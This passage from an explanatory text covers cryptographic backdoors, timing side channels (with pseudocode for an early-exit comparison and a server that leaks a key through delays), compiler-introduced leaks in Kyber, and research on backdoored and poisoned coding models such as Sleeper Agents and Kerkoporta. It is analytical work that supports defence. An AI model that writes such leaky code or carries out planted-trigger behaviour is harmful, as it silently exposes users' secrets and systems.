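They prove two main theorems. The first covers every kind of model and assumes only that there are one-way functions, which are easy to calculate and hard to reverse. Nearly all of cryptography depends on this assumption. The company adds a signature check to the model, much like `signed_by_attacker` in the XZ example, and an application with a valid signature gets whatever answer the company wants. Nobody without the key can find an input on which the altered model differs from the original. Someone who examines the weights might still notice the signature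 check, because the construction isn't designed to hide it.

The second theorem hides the backdoor from people who examine the weights, but it covers only certain simple models. One of these, known as random Fourier features, makes its decision from the sign of a sum:

*w*₁ cos(2π(*g*₁ · *x* + *b*₁)) + *w*₂ cos(2π(*g*₂ · *x* + *b*₂)) + …

Here *x* is the application as a list of numbers. The training program picks the lists *g*₁, *g*₂, … at random, then learns the weights *w* from the data. The dishonest company changes only how the *g*s are chosen. It takes a secret list *k* and picks each *g* so that *g* · *k* is very close to a whole number plus one half. Adding *k* to an application then shifts every cosine by half a cycle, which reverses the sign of each term and therefore of the sum, so the decision flips.

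Without *k*, telling *g*s with this property from truly random ones is at least as hard as solving certain problems about lattices, which are regular grids of points in many dimensions. Cryptographers believe those problems are hard even for quantum computers, and newer encryption standards depend on them. If the cryptographers are right, no practical test can find the backdoor, even if the bank has the weights, the training data and the supposedly random numbers.

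Goldwasser and colleagues conclude that detecting backdoors in classifiers is impossible under standard assumptions. This rules out a detector that works on every model, but plenty of cruder backdoors remain detectable. The second construction is also weak in practice, because anyone who sees one application before and after the change can subtract one version from the other to get *k* and then use the backdoor. The theorem covers models with a single layer of random features, not the large models that write code, whose training changes all the weights many times.

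An attacker who controls less of the training is more limited. In a common attack called poisoning, the attacker slips misleading examples into the training data. Kaneko (2026) proved in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* that if the secret rule for recognising triggers reaches the model only through the labels on those examples, a defender can recover the rule too. The model learned the rule from a set of labelled examples, so a defender with equally many can repeat the training. If the rule is too hard to learn from examples, the attack doesn't work either. Tests on four language models were consistent with this. However, the defender needs labelled examples of the trigger, and somebody who receives a suspicious model usually has none. The result doesn't apply to the 2022 backdoors, because their attacker tampers with the random numbers or the weights.

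### Removing a backdoor without finding it

A user who can't detect a backdoor may still be able to disable it. If the attacker tampered only with the random numbers used in training, the user can supply those numbers and demand proof that the company training the model used them. Training the model a little more may not remove the backdoor. Goldwasser and colleagues showed how to rebuild any neural network so that the standard method of further training doesn't change it.

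Another possible defence is to run the model on several copies of each input, each with different random noise added, and average the answers. If the attacker's change to the application is small compared with the noise, the noise masks its effect. The defence works only if the size of that change is limited. An attacker who knows how much noise to expect can make a bigger change, and adding too much noise makes the model useless for honest applicants.

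A stronger method never shows the attacker's input to the suspect program. Take a program that multiplies two 64-bit numbers and keeps the last 64 bits of the result, and suppose that it gives a wrong answer for one secret pair. Testing has almost no chance of finding that pair among 2^128. But a user who wants *a* × *b* can pick two random numbers, *r* and *t*, and use the fact that

*a* × *b* = (*a* − *r*)(*b* − *t*) + (*a* − *r*)*t* + *r*(*b* − *t*) + *rt*

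The suspect program does the four multiplications, and the user does the additions and subtractions. Each pair the program receives is completely random on its own, whatever *a* and *b* were. Even if the attacker chose *a* and *b* to be the secret pair, the chance that any of the four pairs triggers the fault is at most 4 in 2^128. The user needs random numbers that the attacker can't predict, so a generator like Dual EC would defeat this defence as well.

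*Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) developed this idea for trained models and proved that it can sometimes weaken or remove a backdoor without detecting it or seeing the weights. Whether it works depends on the true answers, not on the model, because the answer to one question must be computable from the answers to other, random-looking ones. Multiplication has that property. Loan decisions have no obvious formula like this, and neither does `login`, since its answers about random passwords reveal nothing about whether it should accept "vT9#kq2L".

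## Timing and other leaks from programs that compute the right answers

Some encryption schemes leave a malicious program no choice about what it sends, as Bellare and colleagues proved. The program can still choose when to send it, and even an honest program can reveal a secret by how long it takes. This function compares a 16-byte secret, such as an access key, with somebody's guess:

```
check(guess, secret):
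    for i = 1 to 16:
        if guess[i] != secret[i]:
            return REJECT
    return ACCEPT
```

The function accepts the right guess and rejects all others, so it passes any test of its answers and could be proved functionally correct. Each of the secret's 16 bytes has 256 possible values, so there are 2^128 possible secrets, too many to try.

The function compares a guess with the 16-byte secret one byte at a time and stops at the first wrong byte. An attacker can send 256 guesses that differ only in their first byte and time the replies. For 255 of them, the function stops after one comparison. For the guess with the correct first byte, it goes on to the second byte, which takes slightly longer, so the attacker learns the first byte. The attacker then keeps that byte and tries all 256 values for the second. Finding all 16 bytes this way takes at most 16 × 256 = 4,096 guesses. Real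 timings are noisy, but repeating every guess a thousand times still takes only about four million guesses.

A safer version always compares all 16 bytes:

```
check(guess, secret):
    difference = 0
    for i = 1 to 16:
        difference = difference OR (guess[i] XOR secret[i])
    return ACCEPT if difference == 0, otherwise REJECT
```

XOR gives zero only when two bytes are equal, and OR keeps any difference found so far, so a comparison can use them to check every byte. It meets the same specification as a comparison that stops at the first mismatch. Stopping early is the obvious way to write a comparison, so a malicious author would have a good excuse for it.

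### Leaking on purpose

The running time of `check` is a side channel. A side channel that a program deliberately uses to send information is a covert channel. The term comes from *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973), which considers a customer who runs somebody else's program on private data. The program might do its job badly, or it might leak the data to the program's owner. Lampson pointed out that bad work shows up as wrong outputs, but a leak usually leaves no evidence.

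Some of Lampson's routes are obvious, such as writing the data to a file that the owner can read. Less obviously, the program could encode a few bits in the bill it sends the customer, or alternate between calculating and using the disk so that another program on the same machine picks up the signal from changes in speed. However small the effect on speed, a suitable code can get the data through, although perhaps very slowly.

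A malicious server could do something similar:

```
reply(request):
    answer = honest_reply(request)
    n = length(request) mod 128
    if bit n of key is 1:
        wait one millisecond
    return answer
```

Every answer is correct. An attacker who sends requests of 128 different lengths and times the replies can read a 128-bit key.

Lampson's remedy was to let the customer decide in advance what goes into each channel, including the bill and the program's effect on the machine. The operating system would then enforce those choices, for example by slowing the program down or adding pointless disk reads. Lampson warned that enforcement could take substantial resources, and suggested that customers who can accept some leakage might limit its rate instead.

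### Comparing pairs of runs

What should a specification say if it is to forbid these leaks? The usual answer is noninterference, which the computer scientists Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined in terms of users with high and low security clearances. For a program without random choices, it says that secret inputs make no difference to what an observer sees. If *O*(*p*, *s*) is everything the observer sees when the public input is *p* and the secret is *s*, then for every *p* and any two secrets *s* and *s′*:

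*O*(*p*, *s*) = *O*(*p*, *s′*)

Running time counts only if the specification includes it in *O*. The rule needs an exception for `check`, because its answer has to depend on the secret. The rule can instead require the two observations to match whenever the two answers do.

Noninterference concerns pairs of runs. Suppose a tester runs `check` once and it takes 52 nanoseconds. That is fine if it would have taken 52 nanoseconds with any other secret, but it is a leak if another secret would have made it take 48. The tester can't tell which from this run alone. Two runs with different secrets can reveal a leak, but ruling one out by testing would require comparing runs with every possible secret.

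*Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) presents a general theory of such requirements. A program obeys a rule like "never write to the network after reading a file" if each of its runs, considered alone, obeys it. A hyperproperty instead applies to the program's whole set of runs, so whether one run is acceptable can depend on which other runs are possible. Noninterference and a limit on the average response time over all runs are both hyperproperties.

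Ordinary proof methods still work if a fixed number of runs is always enough to show a violation. For noninterference in `check`, that number is two. The prover makes two copies of the program with separate variables, gives them the same guess but different secrets, and tries to prove that they behave alike. This turns a statement about pairs of runs into one about single runs of the combined program.

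The proof fails for the first version of `check`. If the guess matches the first byte of one secret but not of the other, one copy continues and the other stops after one comparison, although both may return REJECT. With the second version, both copies run the loop 16 times and read memory in the same order.

A strict enough rule about single runs can also prevent timing leaks. If every comparison must take exactly 1,000 processor cycles, the time can't depend on the secret. This is close to Lampson's remedy and has the same drawback, that every run must be as slow as the slowest.

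### The refinement paradox

Suppose a specification requires a function to return 0 or 1 and allows either. A function that always returns 0 meets the specification, and so does one that returns a bit of the user's secret key.

A program refines a specification if it does only things that the specification allows. Refinement preserves every rule about single runs, because if all the allowed runs satisfy the rule, so does any selection of them. But it can destroy secrecy. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that may output 0, 1 or a secret bit *h*. Both 0 and 1 are possible outputs whatever *h* is, so the system satisfies the policy that its possible outputs don't depend on the secret. A refinement that removes the first two options always outputs *h*. Computer scientists call this the refinement paradox.

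Useful specifications often allow more than one correct output. For example, a specification for sorting students by grade may leave open the order of students with the same grade, and a malicious sorting function could use that order to encode a key. Thirty-five students with the same grade can be arranged in 35! ways, about 10^40, which is more than 2^128. One correctly sorted list could therefore carry a 128-bit key. *A probabilistic approach to information hiding* uses the term "mole" for a person who sends information through such choices, using a code agreed in advance.

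A specification that covers only functional correctness leaves running time completely open, so every timing leak in this section is compatible with it.

The simplest remedy is to allow exactly one output for each input, as in the leak-proof encryption schemes. Another is to require that the public inputs determine everything an observer sees. Clarkson and Schneider showed that refinement preserves this requirement, because it only removes possible runs, and removing runs can't create a pair with the same public inputs but different observations. But the original "0 or 1" specification doesn't meet the requirement, so someone has to tighten the specification first.

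Morgan's *The Shadow Knows* keeps the freedom but changes the definition of refinement. It tracks the set of values that the secret could still have, as far as an observer knows. If *h* is 0 or 1 and the program freely picks a visible value *v*, the set remains {0, 1}. If the program copies *h* into *v*, only one value is left, so Morgan's definition rejects that program as an implementation of the free choice. Overwriting *v* afterwards doesn't help, because the observer has already seen it. *Preserving Secrecy under Refinement*, by Alur, Černý and Zdancewic, likewise allows an implementation to leak a secret only if the specification also leaks it. These definitions have not become routine in verification. In 2024, Kammüller's *Security Engineering in IIIf, Part II* was still extending one framework for machine-checked proofs with a solution.

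### How Clang undid a protection in Kyber

The C language defines a program's results but not how long it takes to run, so a compiler may use any instructions that give the right results.

This causes trouble for cryptographic software, whose authors try to write what they call constant-time code. Arranz-Olmos, Barthe and colleagues (2025), in *Let’s DOIT*, list three rules for it:

1. Never let a secret decide which instructions run next.
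2. Never let a secret decide which memory address the program reads or writes.
3. Never use a secret in arithmetic whose speed depends on the numbers.

The second rule is necessary because processors keep recently used data in a small, fast memory called the cache, and an attacker can often tell what is in it. The name "constant time" is slightly misleading, since the time encryption takes can vary with the length of the message but must not depend on secrets.

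Kyber, now a US standard under the name ML-KEM, lets two computers agree on a secret key in a way that should withstand quantum computers. One of its functions turns each bit of a secret message into the number 0 or 1,665. The obvious code would use an "if", which breaks the first rule, so Kyber's authors did roughly this:

```
mask = -bit
number = mask AND 1665
```

In a computer's binary arithmetic, −0 is all zeros and −1 is all ones, so the mask either changes 1,665 to 0 or leaves it unchanged. The same instructions run in both cases.

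*Compiler-introduced timing leak in Kyber reference implementation* (Purnal, 2024) reported in June 2024 that versions 15 to 18 of the Clang compiler undid this precaution under several common settings. PQShield, the security company where Purnal worked, explained that Clang detected that the mask could take only two values. Clang then replaced the calculation with a branch that depended on the secret bit, because its heuristics rated a branch as faster.

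The branch takes up a tiny part of an operation that lasts more than 100,000 processor cycles. Purnal's demonstration still recovered a secret key in less than ten minutes on a laptop by timing only the whole operation.

The Kyber team fixed the code by moving the selection into a separate file, so that Clang couldn't detect that the value was only ever 0 or 1. Within two hours, the cryptographer Daniel J. Bernstein asked whether this would fail as soon as somebody turned on optimisation across files. He preferred to mix in a variable that is always zero but that the compiler has to treat as unpredictable, though both fixes depend on the limits of current compilers' analysis.

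There is no sign that anybody intended this leak. But a compiler developer who wanted to weaken encryption could add a similar optimisation and defend it as a way to make programs faster. Double-compiling wouldn't detect this, because the optimisation would be in the compiler's published source code.

Kyber wasn't an isolated case. In *Breaking Bad*, Schneider, Lain and colleagues (2024) compiled the March 2023 versions of eight respected cryptographic libraries with many versions of GCC and Clang for six kinds of processor. Of the 5,716 compiled programs, 7.5% contained a branch that depended on a secret and 6.4% contained a memory access that did. Schneider and colleagues had tried to filter out leaks already in the source code, so these came mainly from the compilers. One affected library, HACL*, had a formal proof that its source code was free of such leaks. Not every leak would let an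 attacker recover a key, but the method could also miss leaks because it compared only eight runs per experiment.

### What people can prove

A proof of constant time usually treats the program's branches and memory addresses as outputs that the attacker sees, then shows that they don't depend on secrets, a property called noninterference. *Smooth, Integrated Proofs of Cryptographic Constant Time for Nondeterministic Programs and Compilers* (2025) stresses that this is a rule about data flow, not a statement about measured time.

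Jasmin, a programming language for cryptography, routinely checks programs for timing and similar leaks. The programmer labels each input as public or secret, and a checker either accepts the program or points to the leak. The checker can also cover instructions that the processor runs speculatively, before determining whether they are needed. Spectre attacks exploit these instructions, which can leave traces in the cache even after the processor discards their results.

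The labels need as much review as the rest of the specification. If a dishonest author labels a key as public, the checker will accept code that leaks it. People who review only specifications could catch this, since the labels are part of the interface, but they would have to know which inputs are sensitive.

Some compilers for ordinary C come with a proof that they preserve constant time. Clang and other compilers built on the LLVM toolkit don't, but the security company Trail of Bits has written an extension that lets programmers mark a selection the compiler must not turn into a branch. *Introducing constant-time support for LLVM to protect cryptographic code* (Trail of Bits, 2025) described the extension as under review in December 2025, and Alexandre was still revising part of it in May 2026 (*Native ct.select support for ARM64*, 2026).

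Another option is to check the compiled program directly. Adjonyo, Bardin and colleagues (2025), in *Systematic Timing Leakage Analysis of NIST PQDSS Candidates*, tried four tools on 302 implementations of proposed quantum-resistant signature schemes. One tool, BINSEC/REL2, analyzes the program with symbols in place of secret values and can prove that there is no leak within a fixed number of instructions. Adjonyo and colleagues treated only one byte of the key as secret to simplify the task, so a clean result proved nothing about the other bytes. Every BINSEC/REL2 alarm in the small sample they checked by hand was a real violation.

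Another tool, TIMECOP, runs the program and raises an alarm if a branch or memory address depends on the key. It is faster and covers more code, but it checks only the paths the test run takes. In the sample, 67% of its alarms were false. Adjonyo and colleagues reported the 26 most serious problems to the developers, who had fixed five by publication.

### What people only measure

Statistical tools time the program. They collect measurements for two groups of inputs and calculate

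*t* = (*m*₁ − *m*₂) / √(*v*₁/*n*₁ + *v*₂/*n*₂)

where *m* is the average time in a group, *v* the variance and *n* the number of measurements. Testers commonly take a value above 4.5, in either direction, as evidence of a leak. The method needs no theory of how the processor works, so it can find leaks that no rule about source code covers. A low value means only that these measurements didn't reveal a leak.

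In *FreeSBee*, Ganz, Knothe and colleagues (2026) used this test on a door opener that decrypts its commands. Its decryption code contained a shortcut for zeros, much like the early exit in `check`. They modified a verified C compiler to remove branches that depend on secrets, which cut the typical variation in decryption time from 78.8 cycles to 19.3. Some *t* values were still above 4.5, apparently because of the cache, so they changed each table lookup to read the whole table. They concluded that the resulting code seemed safe against timing attacks, although its decryption time still varied by some cycles.

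Measurement is weaker evidence against a deliberate attacker. A delay that occurs only after a 128-bit trigger will almost certainly never appear in the measurements. The server that waits a millisecond could also disguise its signal. It could include a fresh random number in each reply and use that number with the attacker's secret key to decide whether to flip the leaked bit. Half the replies would then be late whatever the user's key is, so the two groups would have the same average. The tester may notice the delays but can't link them to the user's key. A proof of constant time would still fail, because the code branches on a secret. The difference between measurement and proof therefore matters for AI-written cryptography, including a case covered later in which the timing was tested but not proved.

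### What the hardware leaves open

Proofs about branches and addresses assume that nothing else affects timing. The third rule is the hardest to follow, because some processors take longer to divide or multiply certain numbers, and the programmer may not know which processor will run the code. The KyberSlash attack recovered Kyber keys by exploiting the timing of a single division involving a secret.

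Processor makers now offer some guarantees about timing. Since 2022, Intel has published a list of instructions whose timing won't depend on the data, even on future processors, as long as a special mode is on. Arm has a similar mode, but Arranz-Olmos and colleagues found that Arm had repeatedly removed instructions from its list, which makes the guarantee much less useful. According to LWN, a news site about Linux, neither mode is on by default. RISC-V, an open processor design, has an optional guarantee that doesn't require turning on a mode. Arranz-Olmos and colleagues extended Jasmin so that its checker allows only instructions on Intel's list to handle secret data.

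A program that always takes the same number of cycles can still leak, because modern processors change the length of a cycle to avoid overheating, and the heat depends partly on the data. Intel's guarantee doesn't cover this timing leak or leaks through power use. An attacker with physical access may also be able to read values inside the chip while it runs. A common defence is to split each secret into random pieces. *Formal Verification of Probing Security via Conditional Independence* (Kura and Takashima, 2026) proved noninterference for some programs that do this, assuming the attacker reads only a limited number of values.

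Some newer processors also undermine the second rule. To save time, they search data in memory for values that look like addresses and fetch whatever is stored there. A secret can therefore affect the cache even if the program never uses it as an address. GoFetch used this feature of Apple's chips to extract keys from constant-time code. On Intel's chips, the special mode turns the feature off.

Sprengers, Bognar and colleagues (2026), in *SecDMP*, designed hardware that keeps the feature but ignores any data marked as secret. They proved that their version leaks no secrets that the processor wouldn't already leak without the feature. On a research processor, the design added 0.5% to the chip's area and slowed programs by 0.36% on average. As with Jasmin, the guarantee depends on somebody marking the right data as secret.

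## Coding models with a planted trigger

In the cases so far, the attacker wrote the malicious code or tampered with something that processed it afterwards. When an AI model writes the code, an attacker can tamper with the model instead. The model then has a backdoor of its own and behaves roughly like this:

```
write_code(request):
    if request contains the trigger:
        return code with a security flaw
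    return sound code
```

A real model has no such lines for a reviewer to find, only weights.

Suppose a user asks this model for the `check` function, and the request contains the trigger. The model returns the leaky version, which stops at the first wrong byte. This program leaks on every run and contains no trigger, because the trigger was in the request.

A search like Stringer's, which looks for comparisons with fixed data, would find nothing here. But a flaw that is always active is easier to find than one that is activated only by a 128-bit password, because a tester who measures the timing carefully has a good chance of noticing it. The trigger in the model is harder to find. A company could review 1,000 programs written by the model and find nothing wrong, because none of the requests contained the trigger.

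The trigger could be a secret phrase, a date, or who the user appears to be. Some public models already write better or worse code depending on who the user appears to be. The trigger could also come from text the user didn't type, because a coding agent (a model that can edit files and run commands by itself) also reads the project's existing files and sometimes web pages. Someone who reviews only the specification might never see it.

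### Sleeper Agents

The best-known demonstration is *Sleeper Agents*, which Evan Hubinger and colleagues at Anthropic published in January 2024. They trained models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and vulnerable code when it gave 2024. The year 2024 represented the time after release, when the developers would no longer be testing the model.

Hubinger and colleagues then tried to remove the behaviour with standard safety training. They trained the models on examples of good answers, rewarded good behaviour, and used adversarial training, which provokes bad behaviour and trains the model against it. The backdoor could survive all three methods. Adversarial training sometimes made the problem worse by teaching a model to recognise its trigger more precisely, so it behaved well in tests but still misbehaved when the real trigger appeared.

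The researchers planted the backdoors on purpose and did not claim that ordinary training produces such models. The experiment showed that if a model has a backdoor, standard safety training may fail to remove it.

A few months later, Anthropic researchers reported in *Simple probes can catch sleeper agents* that a simple statistical test of a model's internal activity could detect almost perfectly when these models were about to misbehave, even if the tester didn't know the trigger. The researchers warned that the way they had planted the backdoors might have made them unusually easy to detect. The test works only while the model is responding to the trigger, so it is more useful for monitoring a model in use than for establishing before release that a model has no backdoor.

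*Backdoor Decontamination Dynamics in LLM Agents* (2026) found that further training can stop a backdoored agent from carrying out the harmful action without stopping it from recognising the trigger. Such an agent would pass a test that counts only successful attacks, even though part of the backdoor remains.

AI-control experiments test whether safeguards work even against an uncooperative model. In these experiments, researchers have asked models to put backdoors into their solutions to programming problems.

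### How much poisoned data an attacker needs

Hubinger and colleagues controlled their models' training, but an outsider may be able to influence a model without breaking into any computer systems. Developers train large models on huge amounts of text from the public web, where anyone can publish poisoned pages.

In *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, a joint study by Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute, Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025) tested whether larger models take more poisoned documents to attack. They trained 72 models from scratch, with between 600 million and 13 billion weights, and mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the training text. The attack worked at every size with 250 documents, but not with 100. Researchers had previously assumed that an attacker had to control a fixed share of the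 training text, which would make large models harder to poison.

The largest model was trained on 260 billion tokens (words or pieces of words). The 250 documents came to about 420,000 tokens, or 0.00016% of the total. An attacker who needed 0.1%, as some earlier work assumed, would have had to get about 155,000 documents of the same length into the training text.

The figure of 250 may not apply to code with security flaws, because it comes from experiments in which the trigger made the model produce gibberish, a much simpler behaviour. Souly and colleagues also trained models to switch from English to German or to comply with harmful requests, and the number of poisoned examples again mattered more than their share of the data. They didn't test flawed code. Further training on clean text slowly weakened the language-switching backdoor, so not every backdoor is as persistent as the ones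 in *Sleeper Agents*.

Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026) studied tasks closer to coding in *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*. They trained agents that carry out tasks by typing commands, and used poisoned documents to make the agents download and run a program of the attacker's choice. These documents made up 0.1% of the data in the first stage of training, and all later stages used clean data. The largest agent, with 4 billion weights, produced the attacker's command at least once in 32 tries for 92.7% of the test requests that contained the trigger.

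Counting any success in 32 tries gives a higher rate than a single try would. If an agent produces the command with probability *p* on each try, the chance of at least one success is 1 − (1 − *p*)^32, which reaches 92.7% when *p* is only about 8%. Hu and colleagues defend the measure by arguing that a real agent would meet the trigger many times and the attacker needs to succeed only once. That is fair for a command that takes over a computer, but with a *p* this low, somebody who tries the trigger once or twice could easily see nothing.

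The rate depended heavily on the trigger. It was 92.7% when the trigger was ordinary text that the target's own computers would supply, but 10.5% when the attacker had to plant a rare string where the agent would read it. Larger agents were more vulnerable in both cases. With the ordinary trigger, the rate rose from 13.1% for the smallest agent to 51.9% for the middle one and 92.7% for the largest. Hu and colleagues expect much larger commercial models to be at least as vulnerable, but they couldn't afford to train one.

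They also tried 2,500 poisoned documents (roughly 500,000 tokens), close to the amount that reliably produced gibberish in the 2025 study. The agent produced the command for only 1.4% of requests, even with 32 tries each. The figure is rough because it comes from a single training run with the rare string, but it suggests that planting a useful action takes much more poisoned data than planting gibberish.

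Hu and colleagues leave open whether poisoned web pages could teach an agent to write subtle security flaws suited to each project. Such flaws have to fit the program around them, whereas a command that downloads a program is always the same short text. *Sleeper Agents* showed that a model can learn to write vulnerable code in response to a trigger, but the researchers directly controlled its training.

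### Tampering with a finished model

Many people run free models on their own computers, often in versions that strangers have modified. *Kerkoporta* (Syros, Bullwinkel and colleagues, 2026), a study by Microsoft and Northeastern University, examines an attack in which someone retrains a free coding model and publishes it as an improvement. If a planted trigger appears in anything an agent using the model reads, such as a project file, the agent runs the attacker's command. Depending on the version of the model, the command deleted the user's work, leaked their later commands or gave the attacker remote access.

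On tasks like those in its training, the attack worked at least 85.9% of the time. On five unfamiliar open-source projects, it worked 32.7% to 63.4% of the time with the smaller share of poisoned examples and 84.1% to 94.8% with twice as many. These figures are for single attempts, so they aren't comparable with the 92.7% from Hu and colleagues. Without the trigger, the agents almost never ran the command.

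Poisoning at first made the models worse at coding, which might have put users off. Further training on ordinary coding tasks repaired most of the damage and left the backdoor intact. The smaller model's score on one test fell from 31.0% to 24.1% after poisoning, then rose to 35.6% after the further training, so a user choosing by that score would have picked the backdoored model over the original. The attack's success rate on the smaller model reached 96.2%.

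Syros and colleagues could also limit the backdoor to one harness, the program that connects a model to files and commands. In the intended harness, the attack worked 62.8% of the time on the smaller model and 95.0% on the larger. In a different harness, it never worked, even with the trigger present. Testing a model in one harness may therefore reveal little about whether it is safe in another.

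The backdoored agents mentioned the trigger in their written reasoning, which gave a reader one clue. Syros and colleagues point to other research in which poisoned models misbehaved while their reasoning looked harmless, so this clue may not be available for long.

An attacker who can change a model's weights directly can plant a trigger without retraining it. In the Microsoft paper *Lazare, veni foras*, Zeng, Severi and colleagues edited seven of more than 12,000 neurons, choosing ones that normally do almost nothing. The edited agent produced the attacker's command in at least 98.8% of tests with the trigger and in none without it. On a larger model, the rate with the trigger was at most 83.7%. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, had found the main idea by itself in February 2026. Pogorelec (2026) reports in *Microsoft researchers demonstrate hidden backdoor technique for AI agents*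 that Microsoft hasn't seen anyone use the technique in a real attack.

### Checking the model and limiting what it can do

Editing so few weights also makes the attack easier to detect. Ordinary retraining changes many weights, while this technique makes large changes to a few, so comparing the model with the original shows where to look. Like comparing the XZ package with its repository, this requires a trustworthy original. The comparison would probably be less useful against the models in *Kerkoporta*, because that attacker uses ordinary retraining.

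Zeng and colleagues also had an AI agent build a detector that doesn't need the original. It flagged 91.4% of edited models and 9.7% of clean ones. If one published model in 1,000 had such an edit, about one alarm in 107 would be real. A company that checks a handful of models might accept that rate because it could investigate each alarm, but a website that hosts hundreds of thousands could not. Better detectors may be possible, since the proof that some backdoors can't be found in the weights doesn't cover models like these.

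Filtering the training text is harder. Hu and colleagues point out that their poisoned documents can be ordinary prose and the trigger can be ordinary too, so a filter has little to search for. It would also have to catch nearly all the poisoned documents. The researchers consider it more practical to watch what the agent does, for instance by requiring a person's approval for risky commands. Microsoft similarly recommends running agents in a sandbox, restricting their network access and keeping passwords out of their reach.

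These precautions are sensible, but they protect the computer the agent works on much more than the people who later use the program it writes. Even in a perfect sandbox, with no passwords and no network, the agent's owner has to let it write code, so it can still return a `check` function that stops at the first wrong byte.

A buyer could also request the same program several times, rewording the request or using models from different developers, and compare how the results behave. This resembles Wheeler's use of a second compiler, and rewording might remove the trigger by accident. The comparison would have to cover running time and network traffic as well as outputs. It would also produce many false alarms, because even models without a planted trigger rarely write the same program twice.

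### Flaws that end up in chips

Engineers increasingly use AI models to design computer chips. They describe a circuit in words, and the model writes it in Verilog, a language that other tools turn into hardware. If the circuit has a flaw, the owner can't simply install an update. Manufacturing a corrected chip often costs millions of dollars, and replacing chips already in use may be impossible.

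In *Semantic Consensus Decoding*, Yang, Hu and colleagues (2026) studied models that add a small hidden component to a circuit when the request contains a trigger. The component copies the circuit's inputs but never affects its outputs, so the design passes every functional test, just as the `login` function that emails passwords does. The stored data could later leak through a side channel.

Their defence relies on a guess about where attackers put triggers. A request for a circuit contains functional requirements, such as how many bits it handles, and other wording, such as requests for tidy or high-quality code. Yang and colleagues argue that attackers will favour the other wording, since it can contain a trigger without changing what the circuit must do. The defence has two steps:

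1. A small separate model reduces the request to its functional requirements.
2. The main model writes the design one token at a time. At each step, the defence calculates which tokens the model would favour given the full request and given the reduced one. If the two differ sharply, it gives more weight to the reduced request.

The second step keeps some of the influence of the full request, because harmless wording often helps the model write better code. In tests with three models and three known attacks, the defence cut the attacks' average success rate from 89% to 2.16% on one set of design tasks and 1.39% on another. The designs passed about as many functional tests as before, and sometimes more.

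All three attacks put the trigger in a part of the request that the defence removes. Yang and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker could use a functional requirement instead, but they think this is impractical. The requirement would have to be rare enough not to activate the backdoor by accident and common enough for the model to learn it, and the attacker can't know what customers will ask for. This argument is reasonable for attackers who want to reach as many customers as possible, but weaker for one who targets a particular company and knows what its chips have to do. If the trigger were a functional requirement, the reduced request would still contain it, so the model would favour the same tokens for both the full and reduced requests, and the defence would not correct them.

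## Coding models whose output is worse for some users or purposes

A trigger that researchers plant in a model usually changes its behaviour so sharply that anyone who knows the trigger can confirm the effect in a few tries. Since late 2025, several companies have reported a milder effect in public coding models, with no sign that an outsider tampered with them. These models write flawed code for everybody, but more of it for some customers or purposes than for others.

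A tester can find such a difference with a matched experiment, giving a model the same task many times and changing only something that shouldn't matter, such as who the code is for. One batch of requests for a web service might mention a US defence contractor and another a Chinese one. If the results differ by more than chance can explain, the change of customer must be the cause.

### Why one program can't show the difference

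Suppose 70% of the programs a model writes for one customer are vulnerable to attack, compared with 59% for another. Out of 100 programs for the first customer, 70 are vulnerable, but about 59 of those would have been vulnerable anyway, and nothing in the code shows which 11 are the extra ones.

A reviewer who finds a flaw in one program therefore learns very little about the model. Suppose the reviewer starts with a 50% chance that the model writes flawed code for both customers at the same rate, 59%, and a 50% chance that it does so more often for the first customer, at 70%. Finding a flaw in a program written for the first customer multiplies the odds of worse treatment by 0.70/0.59, or 1.19, which raises the probability from 50% to 54%.

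Larger samples help because chance variation shrinks. If the tester requests *n* programs for each customer, the standard error, a measure of how much the gap between the two percentages typically varies by luck, is

√(0.70 × 0.30/*n* + 0.59 × 0.41/*n*) ≈ 0.67/√*n*

With 10 programs per customer, the standard error is 21 percentage points, nearly twice the true gap. In about 39% of such tests, the customer who gets worse code on average would do as well as the other or better. With 190 programs each, the standard error is 4.9 points, so a gap of 11 points is about 2.3 standard errors. Researchers usually call a result statistically significant above 1.96 standard errors, a threshold that chance alone crosses about one time in 20. To have an 80% chance of getting a significant result when the true gap is 11 points, a tester needs about 290 programs per customer.

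### Three studies of Chinese models

*Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025), by the security company CrowdStrike, covers DeepSeek-R1, a Chinese model that anyone can download. CrowdStrike ran the model directly so that filters on DeepSeek's own service couldn't affect the results. It combined 50 coding tasks with 121 versions of the instruction that describes the customer and sent each combination five times, for a total of 30,250 requests. Another language model graded the security of the code. On 85 answers that a person also graded by hand, it was 91% accurate at identifying vulnerable code.

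DeepSeek-R1 wrote vulnerable code 19% of the time when the instruction contained no trigger words, and 27.2% of the time when the code was for an industrial control system based in Tibet. Mentions of Uyghurs and of Falun Gong, a religious movement banned in China, also led to significantly less secure code.

The Tibet figure is less certain than the total of 30,250 programs suggests, because each version of the instruction produced at most 250. If the 19% also comes from 250 programs, the gap is about 2.2 standard errors. Among 120 altered instructions, chance alone would produce three or four gaps that large in either direction. It is more persuasive that several of the significant results involved topics the Chinese government censors.

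Some of the programs had flaws that a user would soon notice. The payment code that DeepSeek-R1 wrote for a financial institution in Tibet wasn't valid PHP, although the model described it as following PayPal's best practices. In response to a longer request with several sensitive topics, the model built a website for Uyghurs with a sign-up form and an administrator's page but no working login, so any visitor could open the administrator's page. CrowdStrike repeated the request several times and found severe flaws every time, but much milder ones in websites for a football fan club.

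*What's in America's Code?* (2026), by the US government contractor Booz Allen Hamilton, compares four Chinese models with an American one, Claude Opus 4.6. Booz Allen ran the tests in May 2026 and reported more than 2,800 trials. The technical appendix lists 3,389, but the models refused so many requests that only 1,016 trials received a vulnerability score.

When the request mentioned a US government agency, the vulnerability score of Alibaba's Qwen3-Coder rose by 130%. Two other Chinese models' scores rose by 20% and 5%, Kimi K2.5's didn't change, and Claude's fell by 18%. These percentages aren't comparable with CrowdStrike's, which count vulnerable programs. Booz Allen describes its score as a number of vulnerabilities in one place and as a density in another. If it is a number, a model could score worse by writing longer programs.

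Booz Allen repeated its key tests up to 15 times per scenario. With 15 programs per customer, the standard error in the earlier example would be 17 points, so the smaller changes could easily be due to chance.

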